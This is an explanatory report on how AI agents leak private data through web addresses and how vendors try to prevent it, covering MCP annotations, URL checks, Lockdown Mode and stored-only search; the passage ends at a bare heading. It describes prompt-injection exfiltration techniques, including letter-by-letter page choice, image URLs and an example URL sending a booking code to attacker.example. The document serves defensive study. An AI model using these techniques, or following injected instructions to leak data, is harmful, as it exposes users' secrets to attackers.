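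A simulated web is much less useful for discovering mistakes that nobody has thought of, because its builders can include only the hazards they know about. Probably nobody would have thought to build a fake shop that publishes its visitors' searches before agents had come across a real one. It is hard to say how much the loss of realism matters overall, but it probably matters less in training, where agents make an enormous number of attempts, than in a final check before release. A developer could do nearly all of its training and testing offline and still run a few live tests, provided that staff watch them as they happen and can stop an agent in much less than 2.5 hours.

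## How do tools declare their reach, and can the label be trusted?

An operator who wants to keep an agent off the live web, or to ask the user before each live request, has to know which tools can make live requests. This is easy if the operator wrote the tools. But many agents use tools that another company wrote and sometimes runs, and the operator may know little about them beyond what that company discloses.

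The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a widely used standard for connecting agents to tools. A tool's author can use MCP labels called annotations to describe what the tool does. One of them, `openWorldHint`, concerns outside systems, but developers disagree about what it means and few applications act on it.

### The four hints

A Model Context Protocol (MCP) server is a program that offers tools to agents. It can run on the user's computer or on another company's machines. The application that runs the agent, such as a coding assistant, acts as the client. It requests a list of the server's tools, with each tool's name, description and expected arguments. Since March 2025, the list can also include four yes-or-no annotations for each tool, defined in the MCP schema.

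| Annotation | Meaning | Default |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | True if the tool does not modify its environment | false |
| `destructiveHint` | True if the tool may make destructive changes, false if it only adds things | true |
| `idempotentHint` | True if repeating a call with the same arguments has no further effect | false |
| `openWorldHint` | True if the tool may interact with an "open world" of external entities, false if its domain is closed | true |

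The destructive and idempotent hints matter only for tools that are not read-only. Deleting a file is usually idempotent, because a second attempt finds nothing left to delete, but sending a payment is not. In the schema's examples, a web search tool has an open world and a memory tool, which keeps notes for the agent, has a closed one.

All four annotations are optional. A client is supposed to assume that a tool without them can change things, destroy things, do further harm if called twice, and reach outside systems. If this assumption is wrong, the user has to approve a harmless call. Wrongly assuming that a tool is safe could let an agent delete records or contact strangers without anyone's approval. In *Quick Fix*, a developer describes running into the cautious default. ChatGPT listed tools that only fetched data from a blogging site as write tools until the developer added the annotations.

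Many tools rely on the defaults. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (2026) examined 195 working servers from a random sample of MCP's official registry and found no annotations on 58.8% of their 2,766 tools. Of the servers, 72 had annotations on every tool and 122 had none. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (Trofimov and Novikov, 2026) found annotations in wide use among 98,291 tools on remote servers, so the rate probably depends on which servers are counted. Even MCP's example server, which developers copy from, had annotations on only one of its 18 tools until a 2026 change by olaservo, *feat(everything): add tool-level annotations to get-annotated-message*.

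### Labelling six tools

Some tools are easy to label, but others are surprisingly hard. A dash in the table means the hint does not matter because the tool is read-only.

| Tool | Read-only | Destructive | Idempotent | Open world | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Live page fetch | true | – | – | true | It only asks to read, but it can contact any website |
| Search through an outside company | true | – | – | true | The query leaves the operator's systems, and strangers wrote the results |
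| Search of a stored copy of the public web | true | – | – | unclear | Nothing leaves, but strangers wrote the pages |
| Search of the user's private notes | true | – | – | false | The user wrote the notes and keeps them on the same computer |
| Sending email | false | true | false | true | An outsider receives the message, nobody can recall it, and a repeated call sends a second copy |
| Editing a company database | false | true | false | false | It can overwrite records, and a repeated call can add a duplicate, but only in the company's own system |

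Some of these values are debatable. A live page fetch is read-only in the limited sense that GET is "safe", so an operator who lets the agent open any address could reasonably set read-only to false.

Tools that send email are hard to label. MCP contrasts destructive changes with additive ones, and sending a message only adds something, so under MCP's wording `destructiveHint` should be false. OpenAI's developer guide *Define tools* instead applies the hint to outcomes that are irreversible or hard to reverse. That definition fits email better, and setting the hint to true is the more cautious choice.

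The label for the database tool depends on where the server runs. The Model Context Protocol blog notes that "external" might mean anything outside a company's network or anything beyond one machine. A company database may also contain text from strangers, such as customer complaints, even though the tool never contacts them.

### One value for two facts

According to the blog, `openWorldHint` covers both where a tool reaches and what it might bring back. The two usually go together, but they differ for a copy of the web stored on the operator's machines. That copy passes the test for stored reads, so its reach is closed, but its content is open because strangers wrote the pages.

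A single yes-or-no value can't show both whether a tool contacts outside systems and whether it returns untrusted content. If the value covers only reach, the client can't tell a stored copy of the web from the user's private notes, and may treat a stranger's text as safe. If it covers only content, the client can't tell those notes from a contracted booking service that returns only trusted data, even though calling the service sends information out. If the value is true whenever either condition holds, the client can't tell a stored copy of the web from a live fetch.

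For a stored copy of the web, setting the hint to `true` is probably the better choice for now, because an unnecessary warning does less harm than a client that treats all page content as trusted. But the client can then no longer tell from the hint that this tool cannot leak the booking code, and preventing that leak was the main reason for using a stored copy.

An operator who controls both the client and the server could also label a tool's reach and content separately. MCP lets authors add their own fields to a tool under `_meta`, so the operator could define `com.example/reach` and `com.example/content`. Off-the-shelf clients would ignore both fields.

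### How developers read openWorldHint

Developers interpret the hint in several ways. Outreach, which sells software for sales teams, sets it to true for every tool in its *Tool Annotations* because each one contacts Outreach's own servers. StackOne, which connects agents to other companies' software, also sets it to true for every tool, because its tools call outside providers. But the *ChatGPT App Store Submission Guide* for a notes app, which users also sign in to, labels the tools for reading and listing notes as closed. A client that compared the two products would rate looking up a sales contact as riskier than reading a note, though the only real difference may be how their developers understood "external".

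GitHub has considered a third meaning for the hint, that a tool's results contain text written by users. In December 2025, *Add open world hints for tools* (omgitsads, 2025) proposed setting the hint to true on about 60 read-only tools for this reason. A reviewer asked whether project boards could be open-world if they exist only inside paying organisations. omgitsads replied that a board's title and description can contain any text, and that whether to trust the people who wrote it is a separate matter. Another commenter noted that true is already the default, but recommended setting it explicitly because some clients treat a missing value differently.

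OpenAI checks annotations when developers submit plugins, which add outside tools to ChatGPT and to its coding agent Codex. But its own documents define `openWorldHint` differently. OpenAI's *Reference* applies it to tools that publish content or reach outside the current user's account. Under that definition, many of Outreach's tools could count as closed. *Define tools* applies it to tools that can "affect public or external systems", so it is unclear whether a tool that only reads public pages is covered. OpenAI's *Plugins* requires it for tools that "interact with external systems", which would include such a tool.

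OpenAI is also stricter than MCP about what counts as read-only. Developers must label any action that sends data outside ChatGPT as a write. Taken literally, this means no plugin tool could count as read-only, because ChatGPT has to send the arguments to the developer's server. OpenAI probably means tools whose purpose is to send something, since its examples are posting messages, sending emails and uploading files. Still, the rule addresses leaks, which MCP's definition of read-only doesn't cover.

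### What clients do with the hints

The most common use of the hints is to decide when to ask the user for approval. A client might run a read-only tool immediately but show a warning before a destructive one. *When Neither Side Confirms* (Yao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) traced the source code of 41 open-source applications and developer toolkits. By default, 32 had no approval step for an ordinary MCP call. Seven asked the user before ordinary calls, although one of these, the VS Code editor, skipped tools labelled read-only. One used a language model to decide. Only Codex CLI, the command-line version of OpenAI's coding agent, based its decision on several of the annotations together.

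Codex CLI asks for approval unless a tool is labelled read-only and not destructive, or non-destructive and closed-world. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* adds that a destructive label always triggers an approval request, even if the tool also has a read-only label. Under these rules, `openWorldHint` matters only for tools that change something. A correctly labelled live page fetch would run without a prompt in both Codex CLI and VS Code, even if a prompt injection had made the agent put the booking code in the address. To catch that leak, a client would have to check `openWorldHint` for read-only tools too. *MCP Tool Annotations as Risk Vocabulary* (2026), a third-party guide to Codex CLI, reports that the hint may lead to extra scrutiny under some approval settings.

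Clients can also use the hints to decide which calls to run in parallel. Several read-only calls can normally run at once, because none of them changes what the others read. For tools that do make changes, a label on a single tool can't show whether the order of calls matters. Trofimov and Novikov explain that this depends on which two operations are involved, and often on the current state of the system.

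Filtering tools by their annotations is less common. In March 2026, the Model Context Protocol blog reported that no MCP client let users do this. The closest equivalent was GitHub's read-only mode, which about 17% of its users had turned on. *MCP Tool Annotations as Risk Vocabulary*, published in April, lists filtering among Codex CLI's uses of the annotations, so this may have started to change.

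### Why the hints are not enforcement

A server's developer writes its annotations, and the protocol cannot check them. A malicious developer could label a tool read-only and closed-world, then have it delete files or send the user's data elsewhere. The MCP specification therefore requires clients to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server.

This rule was a compromise. While developers were discussing the original proposal, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, questioned how a client could use a label it couldn't trust. Basil Hosmer argued that clients should ignore all annotations from untrusted servers, even a tool's display title. Under the final specification, every annotation is a hint, and each client decides how much weight to give it. According to the Model Context Protocol blog, most clients treat installation by the user as a sign of trust.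 That is weak evidence, since users typically install a server for what it can do, without inspecting its code.

Honest developers can mislabel their tools too. The developer of a page-fetching tool does not know what every website will do when it receives a request. Even a correct label has no effect if the client ignores it. Yao and colleagues connected five inexpensive models to a test server through four developer toolkits. The server offered a tool for deleting notes, correctly labelled destructive, and a list of notes containing an injected instruction to delete a note the user wanted to keep. The models tried to follow the instruction 180 times, and all 180 deletions succeeded.

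OpenAI's review adds a check by someone other than the developer. Developers must justify each label in writing, and OpenAI names incorrect or missing labels as a common cause of rejection. In *Clarification needed on rejection feedback*, a developer quotes a notice that some labels did not seem to match the tool's behaviour, and that each had to be explicitly set to true or false. The review should catch many honest mistakes, but a developer who runs the server can change its code after approval. OpenAI tells developers that the labels affect only how ChatGPT presents a tool call to the user.

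### When the labels are still useful

Most labels are probably honest, and a shared vocabulary can prevent accidents even if it can't stop a determined attacker. Yao and colleagues estimated how much labels could help by pairing 269 destructive tools with 25 applications. In 60.7% of the pairs, the tool could run without anyone's approval. That would fall to 5.4% if every application asked for approval unless a tool was labelled read-only or non-destructive. The remaining pairs involve tools that the researchers judged destructive but that are labelled as safe. Some of these disagreements may come from different definitions of "destructive", since the researchers included sending a message.

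The drawback would be many more prompts. Among tools that looked destructive but turned out to be harmless, the share of pairs in which an application asks the user would rise from 32.5% to 82.6%. People who see that many needless prompts may start approving them without reading them. Better labels would reduce the number, which is a good reason for tool authors to add them.

The labels are more reliable when the operator sets them after inspecting the tools. The client can then enforce rules based on them, such as blocking open-world tools once the agent has read private data. In the hotel example, the assistant could open the confirmation email and keep searching stored pages, but would need approval for a live fetch. This works only if the operator uses `openWorldHint` to describe reach and tracks untrusted content separately, such as with trust labels inside the agent system.

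Network rules can make a closed-world label true whatever the tool's author intended. If a server runs on the operator's machine, the operator can cut off its network access. A tool that still works doesn't need to contact anyone, and a tool that secretly tries to send data out will fail. Codex likewise blocks network access by default for the commands it runs, and an operator who turns access on can restrict it to named websites. Codex's web search has a separate setting and uses stored results by default.

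An operator can't do this to a server that runs on another company's machines. Any call to it is a live request under the definitions above, and the operator can't see what the server contacts next. The only firm protection is to keep private data out of the arguments or not to connect the server.

### Labels for each call and each result

MCP's annotations apply to a tool as a whole, so they have to describe the worst thing it might do. For example, a tool that can read and delete files needs a destructive label even when the agent is only reading a file. *SEP-1862* (SamMorrowDrums, 2025), a Specification Enhancement Proposal by Sam Morrow of GitHub, would allow labels for individual calls. Before calling a tool, the client would send the tool's name and the intended arguments to a new function, `tools/resolve`. The server would return labels for that call, such as read-only for reading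 a file.

This check could also help with a cache that fetches missing pages live. The server could return "closed" for an address whose page it has stored and "open" for one it would have to fetch. But the check sends the call's arguments to the server. If another company runs that server, an address containing the booking code leaves the operator's systems before the label comes back. The stored copy might also expire between the check and the call, so a server that returns "closed" would have to guarantee that it won't then fetch the page live.

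A second proposal, SEP-1913, would add labels to results. Morrow and Robert Reichel of OpenAI wrote it based on problems their companies had met when running MCP in production. Morrow's summary lists labels for sensitive data, private data, open-world content and suspected malicious activity, and a field for the content's source. Each item in a list of search results could have its own labels, and sensitivity labels would stay with the data as the agent passed it to other tools.

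Labeling each result separately from the tool would largely solve the problem with the stored web. A server's author could set the tool's `openWorldHint` to false because a call contacts nobody, and set the label on each result to true because strangers wrote the page. Developers would still have to agree that the tool's label describes reach. Result labels also arrive after the call, too late to prevent a leak through its arguments, and they still come from the server's author.

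Neither SEP-1862 nor SEP-1913 is part of MCP yet. SEP-1862 became a draft with a sponsor in February 2026, and an MCP charter from April lists both as drafts. The charter also set up a group to study annotations, but the group's recommendations are not binding. kapil8811 has submitted experimental code for SEP-1913 (*added initial scaffolding files with python ref SDK*), including a sample server for a medical clinic with eight labelled tools. MCP's *Key Changes* (2026), which covers the July release, lists no changes to tool annotations. In late November, the group's page still listed labels on results as an open question, and MCP's index of accepted and final proposals included neither SEP.

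## How can a web address leak data, and what does checking it prevent?

The hotel assistant could leak the booking code just by opening the reviewer's link with `?ref=482913` added to the end. MCP's labels do little to prevent this kind of leak, but OpenAI and Anthropic also check the address before an agent opens it. Their checks block addresses that a model has put together from private data, but do not fully stop an attacker from extracting the data in small pieces through the agent's choice of which permitted addresses to open.

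### Requests the user does not see

An agent can leak data through a web address without calling a tool. Many chat applications display images in a model's answers. If an answer contains an image's address, the application fetches the image as soon as it displays the answer, and the image's server receives whatever the address contains. A prompt injection therefore only has to make the model write an image address that contains the data.

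The security researcher Johann Rehberger reported this problem to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he recalls that in May 2023 Microsoft stopped its Bing chatbot from loading most images. OpenAI added a first address check to ChatGPT in December 2023, but left it out of some places, including the Mac and iPhone apps.

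The same weakness has since appeared in many other products. Simon Willison, a software developer who collects such cases on his blog, describes one from May 2026 in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork. The agent could email its user without approval, and the emails could include images from outside websites. Opening such an email triggered requests for the images, and those requests could give an attacker working download links to the user's files.

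Link previews cause similar leaks. When someone posts a link in a messaging app such as Slack, the app may open the page to show its title and a picture. Willison (2024) warned that an attacker could make a chatbot post a link containing private data, which the preview would send to the attacker's server. Developers can turn off previews for messages their software posts to Slack. But the security company PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, a personal assistant agent, was exposed to this attack by default when used through Telegram.

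In all these cases, a chat application or email display makes the request, so a check built into the agent's page-fetching tool would miss it. Code that the agent runs can also leak data. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT data leakage via a hidden outbound channel* describes a hidden way to send data out of ordinary ChatGPT conversations, even though OpenAI restricts outside access from the environment where ChatGPT runs code.

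### Instructions to the model

The simplest defence would be to tell the model to keep private data private. The Silent Egress experiment by Lan and colleagues compared defences of this kind with controls on the network. The agent automatically previewed any address in the user's message, which put the page's hidden description into the model's context. An instruction in that description presented the leak as a routine connection check and got the agent to send out a private key. The model was qwen2.5:7b, which is small enough to run on a good personal computer. The researchers ran the attacker's server themselves, so they could count the leaks that arrived.

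Defences in the prompt gave limited protection. Network controls, such as allowing only listed sites and analysing redirects, were much more effective. Filters that look for secrets in outgoing requests were easier to evade. When the attacker had the agent split the secret across several requests, the measured leak in any single request fell by 73%, and simple filters missed it.

Lan and colleagues gave the model minimal instructions about the format of tool calls and none about confidentiality, which probably made the attack easier. But they did not disguise the attack, so a more careful attacker might have done better. Their comparison of defences probably applies to other models better than the 89% success rate does, because a network control can block a request whatever model wrote it.

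*The Framing Gap* (2026) found that written rules can work but depend heavily on their wording. A rule against revealing a secret "in any form" cut the leak rate from 31.9% to zero. The rate was 48.8% with a rule that named specific behaviours but lacked this general clause. ChatGPT leaked nothing in 48 valid trials, which is consistent with a true rate of up to about 6%. A model the researchers tested through the developers' interface leaked up to 100% of the time. They could not see inside ChatGPT and do not attribute the difference to any particular safeguard.

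### Lists of trusted sites

An operator could allow the agent to open only well-known websites. OpenAI considers this helpful but incomplete, partly because many legitimate sites use redirects, which send the visitor's software to a different address.

Suppose `travel.example` is on the list and forwards visitors to any address named in a link. The assistant opens `travel.example/go?to=attacker.example/482913`. The travel site replies with a redirect, and the assistant's software follows it to `attacker.example/482913`, which includes the booking code. Software that checks only the first host name would allow this.

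Even a careful company can have such a link on its site. TechRadar's *Three high risk AI vulnerabilities discovered in Claude AI* reports that addresses starting with `claude.com/redirect/` forwarded visitors to any website. Google's ad system checked only the host name, so an attacker could have bought an ad that appeared to lead to Anthropic's site but sent people elsewhere.

Software can fix this particular problem by checking every address in the chain of redirects. According to Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026), the fetch tool in Managed Agents, Anthropic's service for hosting customers' agents, also checks redirects against the customer's list of sites.

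Lists can also fail without a redirect, and Willison gives three examples. Salesforce's list of trusted image sources included a domain whose registration had expired, so security researchers registered it and received data about sales prospects. The default list in Antigravity, Google's coding tool, included `webhook.site`, where anyone can set up an address that records the requests it receives. Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent for office work, allowed connections to Anthropic's servers, so an attacker could supply a key to their own Anthropic account and have the agent upload the user's files there.

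A shorter list would have prevented some of these leaks, but it would make the agent less useful. OpenAI worries that strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

### OpenAI's check of the exact address

By late 2025, a rule stopped ChatGPT from adding anything to an address it had been given. The security company Radware found a way around this rule and described it in *ZombieAgent*. The attacker supplied a separate address for every letter and digit, plus one for spaces, and told ChatGPT to open them in the order that spelled out the secret. To send "Zvika", ChatGPT would open the addresses ending in z, v, i, k and a. The rule did not apply because ChatGPT never changed an address.

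Radware told OpenAI about the ZombieAgent attack techniques in September, and OpenAI released a fix on 16 December, according to BeyondMachines' *ZombieAgent attack techniques exploit ChatGPT connectors to steal data*. The fix limited which links from emails ChatGPT could open, according to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*. A link could qualify by appearing in a well-known public index.

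On 28 January 2026, OpenAI described a general safeguard based on the same idea. It works in four steps:

1. A crawler explores the public web and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When an agent is about to open an address automatically, software looks for exactly the same address in the crawler's records.
3. If the address is there, the agent can open the page or display the image without asking.
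4. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

The check depends on the crawler's independence, because an address that was public before the conversation and came from somewhere else is unlikely to contain this user's secrets. The reviewer's link with `?ref=482913` would fail the check, since the crawler would have had no reason to visit it. The link through `travel.example` would also fail, because the check covers the whole address and not only the host name.

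OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* says the safeguard, called Safe Url, is for cases where an attacker has already manipulated the agent. OpenAI also applies it to pages that its Atlas browser opens and to searches by its Deep Research agent. Search tools can also leak data through an address. Willison describes an attack on an agent from Notion, the note-taking software company, in which stolen data was put in an address and the address was passed to the web search tool as a query.

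OpenAI's threat model assumes an attacker who can put text where the agent will read it and can see the requests that reach a server. The safeguard is meant only to stop the agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address itself. OpenAI does not promise that the page at a permitted address is truthful or free of harmful instructions.

The warning in the fourth step depends on the user's judgement, which may be poor. Willison reports on an Anthropic study of 1,053 paid testers using a coding agent. During each session, the researchers replaced one approval request with a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of the testers refused it. Users might respond better to a warning about a link, especially if it appears rarely, but the study is a good reason to block unverified addresses when the agent can find the information elsewhere.

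OpenAI also published a technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. After reading it, Rehberger called the safeguard a significant improvement, but not a complete solution. One of his concerns was that developers at OpenAI may build a new feature without knowing about the check, as seems to have happened with the phone and Mac apps. He also noted that, as OpenAI acknowledges in the paper, a version of the letter-by-letter trick still works, using addresses the crawler has already recorded.

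### Anthropic's rule for its fetch tool

Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, a guide for developers, explains that Claude may open an address, public or not, only if it has already appeared in the conversation. The address can come from the user's messages, the results of tools the developer runs, or earlier web searches and page fetches. Anthropic warns that some risk remains, and recommends using the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive.

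The newer Chinese edition, Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, specifies that the tool refuses an address that has appeared only in Claude's own output. The tool also refuses an address that seems to contain a password or similar credential, unless the credential is in the developer's standing instructions or the text of a user's message.

The two companies' rules would treat some addresses differently. The table assumes that the developer uses Anthropic's default settings.

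| Address the hotel assistant wants to open | OpenAI's check | Anthropic's rule |
|---|---|---|
| The reviewer's link with the booking code added by the model | Block or warn | Block |
| A new page, never crawled, that the review links to | Block or warn | Allow |
| A well-known public page that the model remembers from training | Allow | Block until the address appears in a permitted source |
| A private link in the confirmation email that includes the booking code | Block or warn | Probably allow if the developer's own tool read the email, unless the code looks like a credential |

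If the private link leads to the hotel, opening it would not reveal the code to a stranger, because the hotel already has the code. But if opening the link cancels the booking, an injected instruction could do damage by getting the agent to open it. OpenAI's check protects better against this, because a crawler would not normally find a private link. Anthropic's rule would be better at stopping an attacker who uses old public pages, if none of the pages' addresses had appeared in the conversation. The attacker can get around the rule by listing those addresses on a page the agent reads.

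Willison (2026) describes how Ayush Paul used a list of links to attack Claude's chat application. At the time, Claude could follow links in pages it had already fetched. Paul built a website where he claimed that AI assistants had to identify their users by name, and he provided a link for each letter of the alphabet. Each link led to a page with more links. By following these links, Claude spelled out the user's name, home city and employer, which it knew from memories of earlier conversations. The website showed these instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would have seen something else.

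Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally. It stopped the chat application's fetch tool from following links in pages the tool had fetched. The tool for developers still follows such links by default, but an operator can turn this off with the `url_sources` setting.

Suppose Claude writes a short program that prints an address containing the booking code, and the developer's computer runs it. The address now appears in a tool result, so the fetch tool will accept it unless it recognises the code as a credential. To prevent this, a developer can use the same setting to exclude results from the tool that runs programs, or from all the developer's tools. Since 7 October, Managed Agents has followed a stricter rule, under which appearing in output from tools that run commands or read files does not make an address acceptable.

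The most restrictive option is to accept only addresses from the user's messages. Willison (2025) had hoped for a rule like this when Anthropic introduced the tool, and was disappointed that the tool also accepted addresses from tool results. Developers can now set this rule with `url_sources`, but the agent then couldn't open pages it found by searching. The rule would also be weaker if users pasted text from strangers into their messages.

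### Spelling out the booking code with public addresses

Suppose the reviewer has a blog with 36 posts, and OpenAI's crawler has already recorded their addresses. The injected instruction assigns one letter or digit to each post, and tells the assistant to open the posts that spell out the booking code. None of the addresses contains the code, so all of them pass the check. The reviewer works out the code from the order of the requests in the blog's log. Rehberger, who described this trick in 2023, points out that a larger website probably has 36 recorded addresses already, and that an attacker could use thousands.

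The number of requests the attacker needs depends on how much information each one carries. A bit is the amount of information in the answer to a yes-or-no question when both answers are equally likely. Choosing one of N addresses conveys at most

log₂ N bits.

A six-digit code has 1,000,000 possible values, so it holds about 19.9 bits, and each choice among 36 addresses conveys about 5.2 bits. Four requests are enough to convey any code because they allow 1,679,616 different sequences of addresses, while three allow only 46,656.

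To use only four requests, the assistant would convert the code to base 36, which writes numbers using the digits 0 to 9 and the letters a to z. In base 36, 482913 is `acm9`, so the assistant would open the posts for a, c, m and 9.

With 1,000 addresses, two requests are enough to send the code. If the reviewer's site has pages numbered 000 to 999, the assistant opens page 482 and then page 913. A site with a million recorded pages could receive the whole code in one request, though a crawler would probably not record a million nearly identical pages on an obscure site.

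Rehberger suggests keeping each response for a few minutes, or preventing the agent from opening the same address twice in a session. He notes that requests may also arrive out of order, which makes the message harder to read. The table shows how many requests are needed to guarantee that any six-digit code gets through.

| What the attacker can use | 36 addresses | 1,000 addresses |
|---|---|---|
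| Repeat visits and the order of requests | 4 | 2 |
| The order of requests, but no repeat visits | 4 | 2 |
| Neither repeat visits nor the order of requests | 6 | 3 |

Without repeat visits, there are 36 × 35 × 34 × 33 = 1,413,720 ways to open four of the 36 posts when order matters, which is still more than the one million possible codes. With 1,000 addresses, there are 999,000 ordered pairs, and a visit to a single page can represent each of the remaining 1,000 codes.

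If the order is lost as well, the attacker learns only which addresses the agent opened. There are 376,992 ways to choose five posts from 36, and 1,947,792 ways to choose six. An attacker who wants a simpler code could use 60 addresses, one for each digit in each of the six positions. The agent would open the address for "4 in first place", then the one for "8 in second place", and so on. This takes six requests, which can arrive in any order and never repeat an address.

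Rehberger's measures do more to protect longer secrets. With no repeat visits and no reliable order, 36 addresses can reveal at most 36 bits in a session, because the attacker learns only whether the agent opened each one. That limit is far too low to leak a typical cryptographic key but high enough to leak a booking code.

Limiting the number of requests, which Anthropic's tool lets developers do, has a similar weakness. A limit of three would stop the attacker with 36 addresses from learning the whole code, but could still narrow it to about 21 possibilities, few enough to try by hand. The same limit would not stop an attacker with 1,000 addresses.

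These figures assume that the assistant follows the instructions perfectly and that the attacker can tell its requests from those of other visitors. Both conditions are harder to meet in practice, especially if the model usually refuses such instructions. But Paul's attack shows that a commercial assistant can leak data in this way, and an attacker may not need the complete secret. A single visit to one of two pages could reveal whether a user has a hotel booking in June.

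OpenAI's check therefore reduces how much an attacker can learn from each request, but some information can still leak while the agent can choose which live pages to open. A stored read prevents this leak because the reviewer receives no request, whichever post the assistant chooses. If the crawler had also saved the text of the 36 posts, the software could check the address and then return the saved copy instead of contacting the blog. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode takes this approach by limiting browsing to cached content.

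## What does stored-only search protect, and what does it give up?

Stored-only search is a setting that lets an agent search an index or cache but never contact the live web. With it on, the hotel assistant could still read the malicious review, but it could not leak the booking code through its page visits. OpenAI offers such settings in ChatGPT, its developer tools, and Codex. In exchange, the agent misses some pages and sees outdated versions of others. The setting also covers only the search tool, so an agent with another route to the internet can still leak the code.

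### OpenAI's settings

The names and defaults differ between products. The table includes two of OpenAI's APIs, the interfaces through which developers' programs use its models.

| Product | Stored-only setting | If nobody chooses |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT | Lockdown Mode, which also restricts other features | Off |
| ChatGPT for some organisations | Offline web search | Usually off, but on in some regulated workplaces |
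| Responses API | `external_web_access: false` | Live search |
| Agents API | `mode: "cached"` | Live search |
| Codex | `web_search = "cached"` | Cached search, except in full-access mode |

OpenAI's *Offline web search for ChatGPT workspaces* describes a setting for organisations with strict rules on handling data. With it on, ChatGPT searches pages that OpenAI has already indexed or cached. If it can't find a page there, the user has to paste the text, upload a file or suggest another address. Most other ChatGPT features work as before.

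OpenAI describes the protection from offline web search more cautiously than the protection from Lockdown Mode. In Lockdown Mode, browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network, according to *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026). Offline web search is meant to "reduce the chance" that a query goes to an outside search provider, depending on how OpenAI has configured the workspace. ChatGPT may not show users that offline search is on, so an organisation that needs the stricter version should ask OpenAI which version it has.

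Stored-only search protects the conversation from everyone except OpenAI. Developers who use the APIs still send their requests to OpenAI, but its model already processes the conversation, so a stored-only search gives the company little new information.

OpenAI added cached search to Codex in January 2026. The *Codex changelog* (2026) called it "a safer alternative to live requests", and cached search later became the default.

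### The reported "indexed" mode

Vaughan (2026), in *Indexed Web Search*, reports that Codex gained another mode, called "indexed", on 22 June in version 0.142.0. In this mode, the agent searches live but can open only pages whose addresses OpenAI's servers approve. Users can't add addresses to the approved set.

OpenAI's guides do not confirm this. *Config basics*, in an edition that uses GPT-5.5 as its example model, lists only cached, live and disabled modes, but that edition may predate the release. OpenAI's guide to search in the Agents API, which includes a test run from September, lists the same three modes but covers a different product. Vaughan cites a specific change to Codex's public code, so the mode probably exists, but the details of how it works come from Vaughan's account.

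If that account is right, indexed mode sends live queries, so it is not stored-only search. It resembles OpenAI's Safe Url check, so if the software fetches approved pages live, the agent could still spell out the booking code through its choice of pages. Vaughan recommends the mode to anyone who switches between cached and live search. That may suit a programmer looking up documentation, but cached search is safer when the agent has private data in its context.

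Vaughan also writes that OpenAI sanitises cached pages before the agent sees them. OpenAI does not promise this in its Codex guides, where it tells users to treat cached results as untrusted.

### Other companies' tools

The AWS search tool described earlier is stored-only by design because it reads only Amazon's own index and cache. AWS also keeps each query and its results in the region the customer sent the query to, so a query sent to its Ohio region is not passed to Oregon. A regional limit alone doesn't make a search stored-only, because a tool could contact live websites from inside one region.

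Microsoft warns that when customers use its Bing-based search, their data moves outside the geographic area and compliance rules that otherwise apply to it. Administrators can manage access to the search tool, but an agent without the tool can't search at all. A stored-only setting would let it keep looking things up. Anthropic's controls on its fetch tool protect in a different way, by limiting which addresses Claude may open.

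### Why Lockdown Mode turns off more than live browsing

OpenAI designed Lockdown Mode for a small group of people, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and says most users don't need it. OpenAI launched the mode for organisations in February 2026 and began offering it to personal accounts in June.

The mode targets the last step of an attack, when the data leaves. The block is deterministic, meaning that ordinary software stops the outgoing request every time, even if an injection has led the model to make it. A model that refuses 99 injected commands out of 100 offers weaker protection, because an attacker can keep trying. OpenAI completely turns off any feature for which it can't give a strong guarantee of this kind.

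Cached browsing would give little protection if the booking code could still leak through an image's address. Lockdown Mode therefore stops ChatGPT from showing images in ordinary answers or retrieving them from the web. Users can still upload images and generate new ones, since neither requires a request to a third party's server.

File downloads have the same weakness. To analyse a spreadsheet from a website, ChatGPT has to request it from an address, which an injection could influence. In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT can still analyse files that the user uploads. Code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace, can normally use the network if the user approves. Lockdown Mode removes that option, which seems wise given how few testers in Anthropic's study refused a dangerous command.

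Agent mode can operate websites, for example by clicking buttons and filling in forms, which it can't do with a cached copy. Deep research opens many pages to answer one question, and Liang and colleagues showed how much a series of link choices can reveal. Deep research could in principle run on cached pages, with poorer results, so turning it off may be stricter than necessary.

Lockdown Mode does not change how ChatGPT's memory works, and a user can turn the mode off for a single chat. If ChatGPT saved the booking code to memory during a locked chat, it might recall the code in an unlocked one. OpenAI expects the mode to reduce the risk of leaks substantially but does not guarantee that it will prevent them all. OpenAI lists connected apps, unforeseen combinations of features and new attack techniques as remaining risks.

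### How OpenAI ranks connected apps

Apps connect ChatGPT to other services, such as email or file storage. On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks live access to these services, and actions that change them, when such access or actions conflict with its protections. In workspaces that an organisation manages, it does not automatically turn apps off, because some essential work depends on them. The administrator has to choose which apps to allow, and OpenAI ranks the options by the risk of a leak.

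| Risk | What the app does |
|---|---|
| High | Reads or writes anything, if the organisation does not trust the app |
| High | Writes through a trusted app when an outsider might see the result |
| Medium | Writes through a trusted app when only trusted people can see the result |
| Medium | Reads from a trusted app |
| Medium | Searches an index of the organisation's material that administrators manage |

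Reading through an untrusted app is high-risk because the request itself could carry the booking code to that app's service. Writing through a trusted app can also leak data. For example, a calendar might email the details of a new event to every guest, including one the attacker chose.

Within the medium group, OpenAI considers reading less risky than writing, because reading leaves nothing behind for an attacker to find. Reading can still bring private data into the conversation, where another tool could leak it, so the administrator has to look at combinations of apps. An email app that only reads is much safer if no other tool can send anything out.

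The ranking is based on the risk of leaks, not other damage. An agent that deletes the company's records through a trusted app may reveal nothing to an outsider, so OpenAI's wording would put the action in the medium group. An administrator worried about lost data would want a separate rule for such actions.

### Three lookups

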